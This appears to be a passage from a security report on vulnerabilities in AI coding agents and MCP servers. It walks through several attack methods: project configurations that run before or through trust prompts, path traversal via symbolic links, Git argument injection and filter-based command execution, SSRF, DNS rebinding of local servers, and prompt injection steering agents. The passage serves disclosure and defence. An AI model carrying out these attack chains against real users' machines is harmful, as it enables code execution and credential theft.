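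A project could run code through Claude Code's startup check of which version of the package manager Yarn was installed, because Yarn loaded the project's plugins before reporting its version. GitLab Advisory Database's *CVE-2025-65099* (2025) credits Benjamin Faller of Redguard and Michael Hess with the discovery. According to MITRE (2025), the flaw affected users of Yarn 3.0 or later, and version 1.0.39 of Claude Code fixed it. In March 2026 Anthropic fixed another flaw (CVE-2026-33068), in which a project could use a permission setting to skip the trust dialog. According to Utevsky, the fix was in version 2.1.53.

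### What an approval has to cover

These cases suggest that a program should get approval for the exact content that will run, before that content has any effect. Developers can get the timing right by moving every risky operation after the approval prompt. Making sure the approval covers the exact content is harder, because a command's effect depends on more than its own text.

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, applies the rule to hooks. According to Daniel Vaughan's *Before the First Prompt* (2026), Codex has computed a hash of each hook since version 0.129.0 and skips the hook until the user has reviewed that exact definition. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes whenever the text changes. But Datadog Security Labs, the research group of a monitoring company, found that the review does not cover the contents of files the hook refers to. If a hook runs a script in the project, an attacker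 can rewrite the script without changing the hook. Any agent that compares only the configuration entry has the same gap.

Environment variables can also change which program a command runs. The operating system finds programs by searching a list of folders, and Datadog's researchers used a project's settings to put one of the project's folders at the front of Claude Code's list. When Claude Code then ran Git, it started a program named `git` from the project instead of the real one. This happened after the user had trusted the project folder but before they had typed anything. The researchers tested version 2.1.185, which was released several months after the fixes for the Check Point flaws.

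The approval prompt also has to show what will run. Cursor accepts links that install an MCP server, and it asks the user for approval first. In versions up to 1.7.28, however, an attacker could craft a link that hid the command from the user, according to OSV's *Cursor* (2025) (CVE-2025-64106, score 8.8).

### The argument over trusted folders

Utevsky tested four coding agents in 2026: Claude Code, Cursor's command-line agent, Google's Gemini CLI and GitHub's Copilot CLI. In all four, a project could start its own MCP servers as soon as the user trusted the folder. "Trust" was the preselected answer, so the user only had to press Enter once. Gemini CLI's trust dialog listed the project's servers by name, Cursor's warned about them without listing them, and the dialogs in Claude Code and Copilot CLI didn't mention them.

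Claude Code's dialog was more informative before version 2.1, when it warned that `.mcp.json` could execute code and let the user trust the folder with its servers disabled. The newer dialog asked whether the user had created or trusted the project, and said that Claude Code would be able to "read, edit, and execute files here". The word "here" understates the risk, because a local server isn't confined to the project folder.

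Anthropic declined the report. According to Utevsky, Anthropic considers the trust dialog the security boundary for everything in a project's configuration, and holds that a user who accepts it consents to all of that configuration. Only commands that run before the dialog cross this boundary, which is why CVE-2025-59536 counted as a vulnerability. Google and OpenAI reasoned similarly about an attack reported in *SymJack* (Utevsky, 2026), in which the user approves a file copy that secretly overwrites the agent's settings. Both treated the user's explicit approval as intended behaviour. Anthropic rejected that report too, but a later version of Claude Code showed the copy's real destination.

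The vendors' view is defensible because a developer who trusts a project usually goes on to build it and run its tests, which gives malicious code plenty of other chances to run. Asking about each setting separately would also make users more likely to approve by reflex. But people also use coding agents to inspect unfamiliar code before deciding whether to run it, and for them the single question comes too early. Gemini CLI's list of servers shows that a dialog can give users more information without asking them more questions.

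Utevsky also points to an inconsistency in Claude Code. If a project tries to switch off the permission checks on the agent's own tools, a red warning appears with "No, exit" preselected. A project that approved its own servers triggered no such warning, although those servers could run any program without the model doing anything. Anthropic replied that the two settings operate on different surfaces and that the extra warning is an additional layer of defence. This reply doesn't explain why starting an unknown program needs less of a warning.

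Another dispute is over how long trust in a folder should last. Immersive Labs' *Claude Code RCE Vulnerability* (2026) describes an open-source maintainer who trusted their own project folder months ago. A stranger proposes a change on a new branch, and the maintainer switches to it and opens Claude Code to review the change. Without a prompt, Claude Code then starts a server that the stranger added, even if the maintainer isn't signed in. Anthropic answered that trust in a folder extends to content the user later brings into it, as in Microsoft's editor, so this "does not cross a security boundary".

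The case resembles the Cursor flaw, in which a user approved something harmless and the approval later covered something else. Cursor had asked about a particular server, so running a different command clearly exceeded what the user had approved. Anthropic asks whether the user trusts the folder and takes a yes to cover future changes to it. Few maintainers would expect that trusting their own project means trusting every stranger who proposes a change to it.

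Immersive Labs proposes that agents store hashes of the relevant settings files when the user grants trust. If a file later changes, the agent would name it and ask for trust again. Immersive Labs concedes that legitimate changes would also trigger prompts and that some users would click through them. Even so, a message that `.mcp.json` has changed would give the maintainer a specific reason to look at a stranger's branch before starting the agent.

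By 24 November 2026, Anthropic's documentation described a separate approval prompt for servers in a project's `.mcp.json`, though some kinds of session skip it. The prompt protects users less if a project's own settings can still answer it in advance. According to a help page from the monitoring service HostTracker, Claude Code remembers the answer for each project, and users can reset it to review a server again after a change. If a change doesn't bring the prompt back automatically, a collaborator could still replace an approved command, as in old versions of Cursor.

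### Whether users can judge the prompts

There is little evidence on how developers respond to trust prompts. Utevsky writes that developers click through generic ones dozens of times a week, but gives no measurements. In the Check Point test, two professional security researchers read Claude Code's dialog and still expected another prompt before a hook could run. An ordinary user probably wouldn't have understood the dialog any better.

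In September 2025, Anthropic's documentation made users "responsible for reviewing proposed code and commands for safety before approval". By November 2026, interactive sessions started by default in a mode where a second model, a classifier, rather than the user, reviews the agent's actions. The documentation also lists measures against "prompt fatigue", which suggests that Anthropic no longer expects users to read every request carefully. But the classifier reviews what the agent decides to do, and a project's server can start before the agent has decided anything, so the trust dialog still depends on the user's judgement.

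### Automated runs with nobody to ask

Many teams also run coding agents automatically, for example to review each proposed change to a project. No user is present to answer a trust dialog, and the machines running the agents often hold passwords and deployment keys.

Until April 2026, Gemini CLI trusted every folder in such runs. If the agent reviewed a stranger's proposed change, it loaded the environment variables that the stranger had put in the project's `.gemini` folder, which could let the stranger run commands remotely. OSV's *Gemini CLI* (2026), which reproduces Google's advisory, gives the flaw the maximum severity score of 10.0 and credits Elad Meged of Novee Security and Dan Lisichkin of Pillar Security. Corgea's *Gemini CLI* lists the flaw as CVE-2026-12537. The advisory doesn't report any attacks.

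Version 0.39.1 of Gemini CLI made automated runs ignore a project's settings until someone has explicitly trusted the folder, as interactive runs already did. This broke existing workflows, whose owners had to decide whether to trust their inputs. The same release fixed a mode in which Gemini CLI approved every action and ignored detailed limits on shell commands. In that mode, a workflow meant to permit one harmless command permitted every command.

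Claude Code also skips its trust dialog in automated runs, which is where Anthropic's argument about consent is weakest. Utevsky found that Anthropic's official component for GitHub's automation service enabled a project's MCP servers automatically, so an attacker only needed to include a malicious `.mcp.json` in a proposed change. In a test on Adversa AI's own repository, the server sent out all the machine's environment variables, including a secret the researchers had planted. Utevsky advises teams to run the agent only on changes that a person has reviewed, and to keep production secrets off the machines that run it.

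### Attacks outside the laboratory

Criminals already use project files in this way. According to Daniel Vaughan, Datadog's report cites a campaign called Contagious Interview, which Microsoft described in March 2026. Fake recruiters sent developers repositories that ran commands when the victim opened the folder in Microsoft's editor. The report also cites three packages on npm, the main public library of JavaScript code, that installed hooks that Claude Code runs at the start of each session.

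Datadog Security Labs' *Before the first prompt* (2026) uses a similar scenario, in which a recruiter sends a job applicant a take-home exercise and asks them to open it in a coding agent. The applicant has an obvious reason to trust the folder and cannot tell from any dialog whether the recruiter is genuine. Vaughan writes that Datadog's strongest recommendation is to open unfamiliar projects in a disposable environment that contains no sensitive credentials.

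## Tool arguments that reach files, commands and web addresses unchecked

An MCP server can do damage even when the user wrote and understands the entry that starts it, because an attacker may have supplied the file paths, command options or web addresses in the calls it carries out.

Whether such a call exposes a flaw depends on the tool's purpose. Sun and colleagues scanned servers for these three kinds of argument but didn't count tools meant to run any command, since their users expect this. A tool is flawed if an argument can make it do something outside its purpose, such as reach a folder the user never permitted.

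The model offers some protection because, as Sun and colleagues note, an agent may refuse or rewrite an openly malicious value. Their software therefore revised its prompts after each failed attempt.

### Folders whose names begin alike

Until July 2025 the Filesystem server enforced its folder limit by comparing text. It put the requested path into a standard form and tested whether the result began with the name of a permitted folder:

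```text
Permitted folder:  /Users/ana/Notes
First request:     /Users/ana/Notes/monday.txt
Second request:    /Users/ana/Notes-private/diary.txt
```

Both requested paths begin with the same 16 characters as the permitted folder's path, so the server allowed both. But `Notes-private` is a separate folder beside `Notes`. The test compared characters without checking where each folder name ended.

Elad Beber of Cymulate, which sells attack-simulation software, discovered this flaw (CVE-2025-53110, severity 7.3). In *EscapeRoute*, Beber asked Claude in plain words to list a folder next to the permitted one, and the server returned that folder's contents. An attacker doesn't have to guess the permitted folder's name, because one of the server's tools reveals it.

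On its own, the flaw exposes only other folders whose paths begin with the permitted folder's path, though people do name backups and private copies this way. To fix it, the test should accept a path only if it equals the permitted folder's path or begins with that path followed by a slash.

### An error handler that reversed a refusal

The second vulnerability Beber found (CVE-2025-53109) exposed the rest of the disk through symbolic links, which are small files that point to another file or folder. A program that opens a link gets whatever it points to. If `Notes` contains a link to a system file, the link's path is inside the permitted folder, but the file itself is elsewhere.

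The server's developers had anticipated this and written a check, which failed as follows:

1. The server asked the operating system where the path really led.
2. It compared the real location with the permitted folders. The location was outside, so the code raised an error, which should have ended the request.
3. An error handler caught the error. The developers had written this handler for new files, which have no real location yet, and it checked the surrounding folder instead.
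4. The folder that contained the link was a permitted one, so the handler approved the original path.
5. The server opened the link, and the operating system followed it to the outside file.

The handler received an error both when a file did not exist yet and when a file was outside the permitted folders. It treated the two errors the same way. A single test with a link pointing outside those folders would have revealed the mistake.

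Someone must still put the symbolic link in place. In Beber's demonstration, a user with few rights on a shared computer created it, then typed requests to a copy of Claude that ran with another user's greater rights. Few laptops are set up like that, but archives and Git repositories can also contain symbolic links. An attacker could include one in a project that the user downloads into the permitted folder, then use a prompt injection to have the agent open it.

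The server has no tool for running programs, but Beber used its ability to write files to get one to run. On a Mac, a file in a certain folder can make the system start a program whenever the user logs in. Beber had Claude write such a file through a symbolic link, and the calculator opened at the next login.

During the tests, the server gave Claude access to a folder that was not on Claude's list of permitted folders. Claude wrote afterwards that the folder was not on the list and that this might be a "security vulnerability".

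Beber reported both flaws on 30 March 2025. Anthropic acknowledged them on 1 May and released a patch on 1 July. The advisories, GitLab's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025) and *CVE-2025-53109* (2025), list versions before 0.6.3 and 2025.7.1 as affected. The CVE record for the link flaw, as reproduced by GCVE (2025), gives 0.6.4 instead of 0.6.3, but version 2025.7.1 is safe according to both. On 2 July 2025 CISA recorded no exploitation of the link flaw, and Exploit Intel's *CVE-2025-53110* shows the same assessment for the name flaw.

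### Resolve the path first, then compare

Security engineers call a path that leads outside the intended folder path traversal. A safe check first finds the real location of the file, then tests whether that location is inside the permitted folder, and then opens the location it has tested. In Python, the check takes a few lines:

```python
allowed = Path("/Users/ana/Notes").resolve()
target = Path(requested_path).resolve()
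if not target.is_relative_to(allowed):
    raise PermissionError("outside the permitted folder")
open(target)
```

`resolve` follows every symbolic link and works out steps such as `..` (the folder above). `is_relative_to` compares whole names, so `Notes-private` doesn't match `Notes`. The permitted folder must be resolved too, because it may also lie behind a link. If a file doesn't exist yet, `resolve` follows as much of the path as exists, so the code doesn't need a separate branch like the one that failed.

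The last line opens `target`, the path that passed the test, not the text that the model sent. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) gives the general rule that the check must use the same form of the path as the tool that will eventually open it. Even then, someone who can change the folder could swap in a link after the test and before the file opens. A sandbox that hides the rest of the disk from the server would also prevent that.

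### A repository limit that the server never applied

The Git server, from the same collection as the Filesystem server, lets an agent use Git. A user can start it with an option that names one repository, and would expect the agent to stay there. But each tool call also contains a repository path, and the server used that path without checking it against the option (CVE-2025-68145). An attacker who could steer the agent could therefore reach any repository the server's account could open.

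Cyata, a company that sells controls for AI agents, employs the researchers who found this. One of them had started reading the code just to learn how official servers work, according to Cyata's *How We Found Code Execution in Anthropic’s Official Git MCP Server*.

A second flaw (CVE-2025-68143) let an attacker do without an existing repository. The server's `git_init` tool, which creates a repository, accepted any folder. Because Git can record and display the contents of files in a repository, an attacker could have the server turn a folder of private keys into one and then read the keys with the ordinary tools, though this only brought the keys into the model's context.

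The same tool could also delete files. Git removes a file from the folder when a user switches to a branch that lacks it. Cyata's researchers found a series of ordinary calls that recorded a file on one branch and then switched to another. A copy stayed in Git's records, but any program that depended on the file would no longer find it.

Anthropic removed `git_init` in version 2025.9.25 because the server is meant for existing repositories, according to GitLab's *CVE-2025-68143* (2025). It did not fix the repository limit until version 2025.12.18. GitLab's *CVE-2025-68145* (2025) describes a repair that follows the order set out above: the server resolves both the configured repository and the requested path, follows any links, and then checks that the path is inside the repository. The advisory covers only servers started with the option that sets this limit, since without it the server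 has no limit to enforce.

### A branch name that Git read as an option

The third flaw (CVE-2025-68144) is an argument injection, like the npx trick that got past Flowise's allowlist. The Git server's `git_diff` tool compares the project with another version, which the model specifies in the `target` argument, normally as a branch name. The server put this value on Git's command line without checking it, so Git would treat a value that began with a hyphen as an option.

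One of those options makes Git write the result to a named file instead of displaying it. An attacker who supplied this option in place of a branch name could overwrite any file the server's account could write to. Usually there were no differences to report, so Git emptied the file. The `git_checkout` tool also passed its argument to Git without checking it.

He and colleagues describe a different flaw under the same number. Their paper presents a dataset of 24 vulnerabilities in MCP software, and its example for this one shows the server running extra commands that an attacker added after the option. That would be shell injection, in which a character such as a semicolon makes the command shell start a second command.

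The published code doesn't fit that description. The server passed its values to Git through a Python library that, by default, starts Git directly without a shell, so a semicolon would have become part of a file name. GitLab's *CVE-2025-68144* (2025) mentions overwritten files but not shell commands, and Intruder lists the flaw under the standard category for argument injection.

The distinction affects the fix. He and colleagues conclude that developers should avoid the shell and use library functions, but the Git server already did that and was still vulnerable. Version 2025.12.18 of the server rejects values that begin with a hyphen, then uses Git to check that the value names a real version of the project. The second check is stronger because it accepts only what the argument is supposed to contain.

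Sun and colleagues describe a real case of shell injection in bytebot, an open-source agent that operates a computer. Its tool for writing files inserted the path it received into a command that a shell ran with administrator rights. A path containing the right punctuation could end the intended command and begin another, and the researchers used such a path to take full control of bytebot's container. Writing the file without a shell would have prevented this injection.

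He and colleagues also give 2025.12.17 as the repaired version and rate the flaw critical. The version number can be explained by an early text of the record, which included the instruction to install 2025.12.17 "when it is released". That text is preserved in *CVE-2025-68144* (2025) from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute. The corrected advisory has 2025.12.18. The rating is harder to explain, since The Hacker News (2026) gives scores of 8.1 on the older version of the severity scale and 6.4 on the newer one, and neither is critical.

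### Two servers that together run commands

On 24 June 2025, Cyata sent Anthropic its first report, which covered the unchecked repository path and `git_init`. The report was marked "informative" a day later, a label for findings that call for no immediate action. The researchers then looked for a more serious effect and found one by adding the Filesystem server.

Git filters run a command on a file whenever Git adds the file to the repository. Developers use them to tidy up text, for instance. The command is stored in a settings file in the repository's hidden `.git` folder. The Git server had no tool for writing this settings file. The Filesystem server could write it, since it is plain text, but had no tool for running commands.

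An agent connected to both servers could carry out the whole attack on the attacker's instructions. It would have the Git server create a repository in a folder that the Filesystem server was allowed to change. It would then have the Filesystem server write the filter into the settings and create a file for the filter to act on. When the Git server added that file to the repository, Git would run the attacker's command.

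The researchers had first tried Git's hook scripts. These failed because Git runs a hook only if its file is marked as executable, and the Filesystem server doesn't mark files that way. Filters don't need the mark because Git passes their commands to a shell.

The result was worse than you would expect from either server's flaws alone, because the Filesystem server treats Git's settings as text in a permitted folder, while Git treats them as instructions. A developer who reviewed only the Filesystem server would have no reason to handle that file differently. Severity scores don't capture this kind of danger well either, because each one rates a single flaw in a single program.

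The repairs don't fully prevent this combined attack. If a user gives both servers access to the same project, as is natural, a repository already exists there and the attacker can skip the first step, so removing `git_init` and enforcing the repository limit make no difference. To prevent this, the Filesystem server would have to refuse to write inside `.git` folders, or the Git server would have to ignore filters. Cyata advises users to review which servers they run together. It also notes that a code editor's built-in ability to write files can take the Filesystem server's place, although some of these routes have since become more restricted.

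The second report, on 6 July, included the overwritten files and the command execution. Anthropic reopened the case on 24 July, accepted it on 10 September, and committed the remaining fixes on 17 December, almost six months after the first report. Cyata doesn't mention any real attackers using the flaws.

### Requests from inside the network

Unchecked paths and options mostly endanger the machine the server runs on. A tool that fetches web pages can also endanger other machines, because the server sends the request. The server can often reach things an outsider can't, such as a company's internal websites or programs that accept connections only from the same computer.

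In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker chooses the address that a tool fetches. On rented cloud machines, the most valuable target is usually the metadata service, an internal address where a machine can look up its own details. Those details may include temporary access keys for the customer's cloud account, which the server may collect and pass to the model.

In August, Ahmed (2026) reported in *Attackers Exploit Critical Flaw in MLflow* that attackers were exploiting a server-side request forgery (SSRF) flaw in MLflow, a platform for machine-learning projects with about 30 million downloads a month. The flaw could expose internal services and cloud metadata to someone without an account. MLflow is not an MCP server, but an SSRF flaw in a fetch tool on a cloud machine could expose the same kinds of resources.

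A developer might try to prevent SSRF by refusing requests to internal host names, but attackers can bypass this check in two common ways.

The first is a redirect, in which a website answers a request with a new address for the page. Most software that fetches pages goes to the new address automatically. Because the check examines only the original address, an attacker can submit the address of a public site that redirects to an internal one.

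The other is DNS rebinding, which the Origin check guards against in browsers. A server uses the Domain Name System (DNS) to translate a host name into the numerical IP address it connects to, and it may do so twice. The attacker's domain first returns a public IP address, and the server approves the request. When the server looks the name up again to connect, the domain returns an internal address.

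*Security Considerations for Model Context Protocol (MCP) Implementations in AI Agent Systems* (Syed, 2026) describes the remedy. Syed Anas Mohiuddin, an independent researcher, wrote it in June 2026 as an Internet-Draft, a proposal that anyone can submit to the body that develops internet standards. It requires servers to check the IP address when they connect and to refuse private and local ranges. By default, a server should not follow redirects. If it does, it must check each new destination in the same way. The draft also recommends limits on outgoing connections in the operating system or container, which still apply if the server's own check fails. The draft had no official standing and expired on 3 December 2026.

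Host names need a rule similar to the one for files because a host name, like a symbolic link, only points to something else. The server has to resolve the host name to an IP address, check that address, and then connect to that same address.

Even a check that looks up the IP address can be faulty. OffSeq's *CVE-2026-141591* (2026), published on 2 December, describes an SSRF flaw in a community-made server, mcp-fetch-server. The flaw is in two functions named `validateUrl` and `validateResolvedIp`, so the developer had evidently tried to prevent SSRF. The entry gives the flaw a score of 9.2 and lists no known exploitation. It affects versions from 1.1.0 onward and was fixed in 1.2.0.

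### Five reports by one researcher

Mohiuddin also looked for SSRF in the servers of large organisations. By October 2026, Google, the bank JPMorgan Chase, the database company Weaviate, the French government's digital directorate (DINUM) and the Indonesian city of Tangerang had each fixed a flaw he had reported, according to *Google, JPMorgan and two governments fixed the same MCP flaw* (Stanciuc, 2026).

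The Google case has the fullest public record. MCP Toolbox for Databases connects agents to databases and other sources of data, including web services. The program cleaned up the values that users supplied, but the part that sent web requests followed redirects without restriction and never checked the destination IP address. NIST's *CVE-2026-14540 Detail* (2026) explains that an attacker, or a malicious prompt, could supply a path that made the intended web service redirect the request to an internal address, and the toolbox would follow the redirect.

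Google scored the flaw at 8.0, taking into account that it knew of no attacks or public attack code. OSV's *CVE-2026-14540* (2026) lists versions 0.3.0 to 1.4.0 as affected. The fix added lists of allowed and blocked IP ranges and protection against DNS rebinding. Google's advisory credits Mohiuddin.

JPMorgan's server searches documentation and has two tools that fetch content. One checked the requested domain against an allowlist, while the other fetched any address it received. The bank had adapted the server from an Amazon Web Services project that never fetched addresses supplied by the caller, so the adaptation introduced the flaw. Mohiuddin rates it as medium severity and says the bank confirmed it and deployed a fix.

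Weaviate dealt with its flaw by restricting a setting to Google's hosts. A short list of permitted hosts is the simplest protection when a tool has only a few legitimate destinations. It would not work for DINUM, whose server for France's open-data platform fetched web addresses that others had supplied, or for any tool that must open pages across the web. These tools have to accept unknown hosts but block internal ones.

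Even blocking internal addresses can be wrong for some users. Mohiuddin's draft cites a public report of SSRF in Microsoft's server for controlling a web browser, which may also have access to the user's logged-in sessions. A web developer may install that server to test a site running on their own laptop, and a strict block would prevent this. Because the right choice depends on the user, the server's developer needs to offer a setting with a safe default.

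Except for the Google case, Stanciuc's details of the flaws and repairs come from Mohiuddin's own account. Mohiuddin also says that five US federal government MCP servers, including one for veterans' benefit claims, still had unresolved findings in October.

### What the five cases can support

In May 2026, Mohiuddin argued that the problem was structural and predicted that teams with no code or owner in common would all produce it. In October he wrote that this argument was no longer a guess, because the problem had recurred at a cloud company, a bank and a national government.

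The five cases show that experienced teams make this mistake, and that they don't just inherit it from one another. The JPMorgan case is the most persuasive, because its developers started with code that lacked the flaw and added it themselves.

Five cases can't show how common the mistake is. Mohiuddin chose which servers to examine, and the list contains only those where he found a flaw and the owner repaired it. Without knowing how many servers he found to be safe, a reader can't tell whether these are five out of six or five out of five hundred. He was also looking specifically for this flaw, and had written a scanner, mcp-safeguard, that tests for it. When he published the draft in June, he had scanner results only from test servers built to contain such flaws.

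The prediction was also a safe one. SSRF was a familiar problem in web software long before MCP existed, and the draft cites other people's public reports about Microsoft's browser server and a fetch server in the MCP project's own collection.

Other people's findings make the selection less of a concern. OffSeq's *Obot* (2026) describes an SSRF flaw in Obot, a platform for managing MCP servers. An attacker could exploit it through the address given for a remote server. GitLab lists another SSRF flaw in ToolHive, Stacklok's program for running MCP servers, scored 4.7 and fixed in version 0.31.0. The security company CloudSEK examined a server that required no login and found that its audio-downloading tool accepted any web address. With mcp-fetch-server, that makes four more teams with no obvious connection to Mohiuddin's five.

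The dataset from He and colleagues has no SSRF category, which seems to be counterevidence, but it contains only 24 vulnerabilities, all with CVE numbers and published by February 2026. It didn't cover projects' public issue trackers, where the reports cited in Mohiuddin's draft appeared.

Some repeated cases are not independent evidence because they come from the same shared code. *MCP Security Research*, by felixbillieres, describes SSRF in the opposite direction, where a malicious server attacks the client. When the client connects, the server demands a login and gives an address where the client can find out how to log in. The official Python and TypeScript SDKs fetched that address without checking whose it was. Claude Desktop and Claude Code were also affected. Anthropic closed the report as a duplicate. If many applications built on those SDKs had the flaw, they would count as one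 mistake, whereas JPMorgan and Google each made their own.

It is also unclear what "structural" means. The draft blames the protocol, but its claim that the MCP specification contains no binding security requirements is too strong, because the specification requires servers to validate all tool inputs. However, this requirement doesn't specify how to validate a web address, and a developer could easily think that checking the host name was enough.

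A simpler explanation is that the shortest code for fetching a page is usually unsafe. Common web libraries follow redirects by default and connect to whatever IP address DNS returns, so a tool is vulnerable unless its developer adds checks. This would explain the flaw in MLflow, which does not involve MCP. MCP may still make the problem worse by encouraging developers to turn many small functions into tools that a model can call with any address. To measure that effect, researchers would need to test a random sample of MCP servers that fetch web addresses and compare the share that are vulnerable with the share among ordinary web applications that do the same job.

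## Web pages and remote servers that reach local agent software

An attacker can also send requests to internal addresses through a victim's web browser. Many agent tools open a port on the user's computer and accept connections only from programs on that computer. This blocks direct connections from the internet, so developers often don't add a password. But the browser also runs on that computer, and any page it opens can contain an attacker's code.

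Remote servers are also a danger, even though the user's own software makes the connection, because the client has to process whatever the server sends back. In 2025, researchers found that a popular client could run part of a server's reply as a command.

### How a web page reaches a local port

A program can contact other programs on the same computer at the address 127.0.0.1, also called `localhost`, with a port number that identifies the program to reach. JavaScript on any web page can make the browser send a request to this address. A cross-site request is a request from one site's page to a different site.

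Browsers restrict these requests through the same-origin policy. Two addresses have the same origin if their scheme (such as `https`), host name and port all match. A page can't read replies from another origin unless that origin permits it. However, the browser often still sends the request, which is enough for an attacker if the request itself starts a program. MCP's own messages are better protected because they are in JSON. Before sending one to another origin, the browser sends a preliminary request, and it sends the message only if the reply permits it.

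DNS rebinding avoids both restrictions. Suppose a developer runs a notes server without a password on port 8000 of their laptop, and then visits an attacker's website:

1. The browser looks up `attacker.example`, gets the attacker's public IP address, and loads a page from port 8000 there. The page contains a script.
2. The attacker changes the DNS record for `attacker.example` to 127.0.0.1.
3. The script requests more data from `attacker.example`. The browser looks up the name again and connects to port 8000 on the laptop.
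4. The scheme, name and port are the same as before, so the browser lets the script read the reply.
5. The script lists the notes server's tools and calls them.

The developer sees only an ordinary web page. Whether the attack works depends on the victim's browser and operating system, according to Tenable.

### MCP Inspector: a proxy that started any program

MCP Inspector, Anthropic's tool for testing servers, has a web interface that the developer opens in a browser. Its proxy, which listens on port 6277, connects the interface to the server under test. If that server uses STDIO, the proxy has to start it, so the interface sends the proxy a web request containing a command and its arguments. Before version 0.14.1, the proxy ran the command without checking who had sent the request (CVE-2025-49596), so web pages could start STDIO servers, which they normally can't reach.

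The proxy accepted connections from every network the computer was on, so someone on the same Wi-Fi could send it a command directly. If the victim opened a malicious web page while the Inspector was running, the page could also send a command, through either DNS rebinding or a cross-site request. The cross-site request worked because the command was part of an ordinary web address, and the proxy's settings let any site read the replies.

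Some developers may not have realised that the Inspector was running. Lumelsky (2025), in *Critical RCE Vulnerability in Anthropic MCP Inspector*, points out that `mcp dev`, a command from the Python SDK's beginner instructions, started it automatically. Lumelsky's employer, Oligo Security, also found copies of the Inspector open to the internet.

Oligo's demonstration page sent its request to 0.0.0.0, an address that can refer to the visitor's own machine. Oligo had publicised this method in 2024, and Lumelsky wrote in June 2025 that Chromium and Firefox still allowed it. Tenable's demonstration used the usual local address, 127.0.0.1, so blocking 0.0.0.0 in browsers would not have been enough to protect developers.

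Tenable reported this flaw first, though Oligo often gets the credit. According to the timeline in Tenable's *Anthropic MCP Inspector Remote Code Execution*, the company asked Anthropic for a security contact on 6 March 2025. The two companies then spent almost three weeks discussing whether Tenable had to report through HackerOne, a platform for vulnerability reports. Tenable sent the details on 26 March, and Oligo sent its own report on 18 April. GitLab's copy of the advisory credits only Rémy Marot of Tenable.

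Anthropic confirmed the fix on 13 June, 11 weeks after it received the details. That was a long time for a flaw that attackers could exploit just by getting a user to visit a web page, though Lumelsky calls the response prompt. The US National Vulnerability Database entry, *CVE-2025-49596 Detail* (2025), gives the flaw a severity score of 9.4 and describes the weakness as missing authentication. Neither Tenable nor Oligo reports attacks by criminals.

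Version 0.14.1 closes all three routes. The proxy creates a random session token when it starts and refuses requests that don't include it. It listens only on `localhost` and accepts requests only from the Inspector's own interface. Developers can turn off the token with Anthropic's `DANGEROUSLY_OMIT_AUTH` setting, which is much like the flag that OX Security later proposed for launch commands in the SDKs.

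Seven months later, a similar flaw turned up in MCPJam inspector, a testing tool from another developer. In versions up to 1.4.2, an attacker could run code by sending a crafted web request to an exposed address, according to OSV's *GHSA-232v-j27c-5pp6* (2026), which scores the flaw at 9.8.

### Rebinding protection that was off by default

The official TypeScript SDK had a similar weakness (CVE-2025-66414). It included protection against DNS rebinding, but developers had to turn it on with the `enableDnsRebindingProtection` option. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-66414 Detail*, a server built with the SDK was vulnerable if it ran on `localhost` over HTTP without authentication and with this option off. A malicious website could then call the server's tools as if it were the user. STDIO servers were not affected.

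The damage depends on the tools the server provides. A website may be able to read the tables on a database server but learns very little from a weather server. NVD lists a severity score of 7.6, and GitLab's *CVE-2025-66414* (2025) gives 8.1 on the older scale. Neither entry mentions attacks.

The maintainers released the fix in version 1.24.0, and the advisory followed on 2 December 2025. Upgrading doesn't protect every server. Servers created with the SDK's helper function, `createMcpExpressApp()`, now have the protection on whenever they listen on `localhost`, but developers who configure Express, the underlying web framework, themselves must add the protection manually. A security scan based only on the SDK's version number would therefore miss some unprotected servers.

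At least four other official SDKs had the same problem. The security company Mondoo's database reproduces an almost identical advisory for the Python SDK and has another for the Go SDK. The Java SDK didn't check the Origin header before version 1.0.0. The Rust SDK didn't check the Host header before version 1.4.0 (CVE-2026-42559), and Mondoo lists that flaw with a score of 8.8.

He and colleagues attribute the TypeScript flaw to gaps in the first version of the MCP specification, which left room for unsafe defaults. Those gaps can't be the whole explanation, because the Java advisory, as reproduced by Mondoo, describes the missing check as a violation of the specification and quotes the rule. A more likely reason is that a server without the check passes every ordinary test, since a developer's own client never sends a request from a hostile domain.

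### Why servers check two headers

While the Origin header names the site behind a request, the Host header gives the host name from the requested URL. In step 3 of the timeline, the request arrives at the laptop with `attacker.example` in its Host header, and the script can't change this. A notes server that accepts only `localhost` and 127.0.0.1 as host names can therefore refuse the request.

The specification requires a server to answer with an error if the Origin header is "present and invalid". Browsers omit this header from some requests that a page sends to its own origin. After rebinding, the browser treats the attacker's requests as same-origin, so they can lack the header and fall outside this rule, but checking the Host header catches them. The gap matters less for new servers because the July 2026 version of Model Context Protocol has clients send every message as a POST request,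 and browsers include the Origin header in POST requests. According to its Model Context Protocol documentation, the Python SDK now checks both headers.

### OpenClaw: a control page that gave away its token

OpenClaw, earlier called Clawdbot and Moltbot, is an open-source personal assistant that can read a user's messages and run commands on their computer. A background program called the gateway carries out these tasks, and the user manages it from a control page in the browser. Unlike the Inspector's proxy, the gateway required a token, and the control page kept a copy in the browser's storage.

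A link to the control page could specify which gateway to use. The page saved the address from the link, connected to it immediately and sent the token, all without asking the user. An attacker could therefore put the address of their own server in a link and receive the token of anyone who clicked it (CVE-2026-25253).

A stolen token is of little use if the gateway accepts only local connections, as most users' gateways do. *1-Click RCE To Steal Your OpenClaw Data and Keys (CVE-2026-25253)* (2026), by depthfirst, a company that sells automated code analysis, explains how a depthfirst researcher got around this by using the token from inside the victim's browser. The attacker's page opened a WebSocket, a connection that stays open and carries messages in both directions, to the gateway on `localhost`. The same-origin policy doesn't restrict WebSockets, so the receiving program has to check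 the Origin header itself, which OpenClaw's gateway didn't do.

OpenClaw normally asks the user before it runs dangerous commands, and users can also confine commands to a container. Neither measure stopped the attack, because the stolen token gave administrator rights over both. When the victim visited the researcher's page, it turned off the approval prompts, switched the agent from the container to the computer itself, and then ran a command, all without further action from the victim.

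GitLab's *CVE-2026-25253* (2026) scores the flaw 8.8 and lists every version before 2026.1.29 as affected. The control page now asks for confirmation before it connects to a new gateway. This stops the link from leaking the token, but it doesn't supply the missing Origin check, and depthfirst doesn't say whether the maintainers added one. Upgrading also doesn't cancel a token that an attacker already has, so depthfirst advises users to replace their tokens if they suspect a leak.

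The security company Ethiack found the flaw independently. Branquinho (2026), in *One-click RCE on OpenClaw in under 2 hours*, reports that Ethiack's AI testing agent discovered the token leak in about 1 hour and 40 minutes without human help. Ethiack reported it on 26 January 2026, and the maintainers fixed the code two days later. According to MITRE, CISA recorded on 3 February that a public demonstration existed but listed no actual attacks.

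### The permission prompt in Chrome

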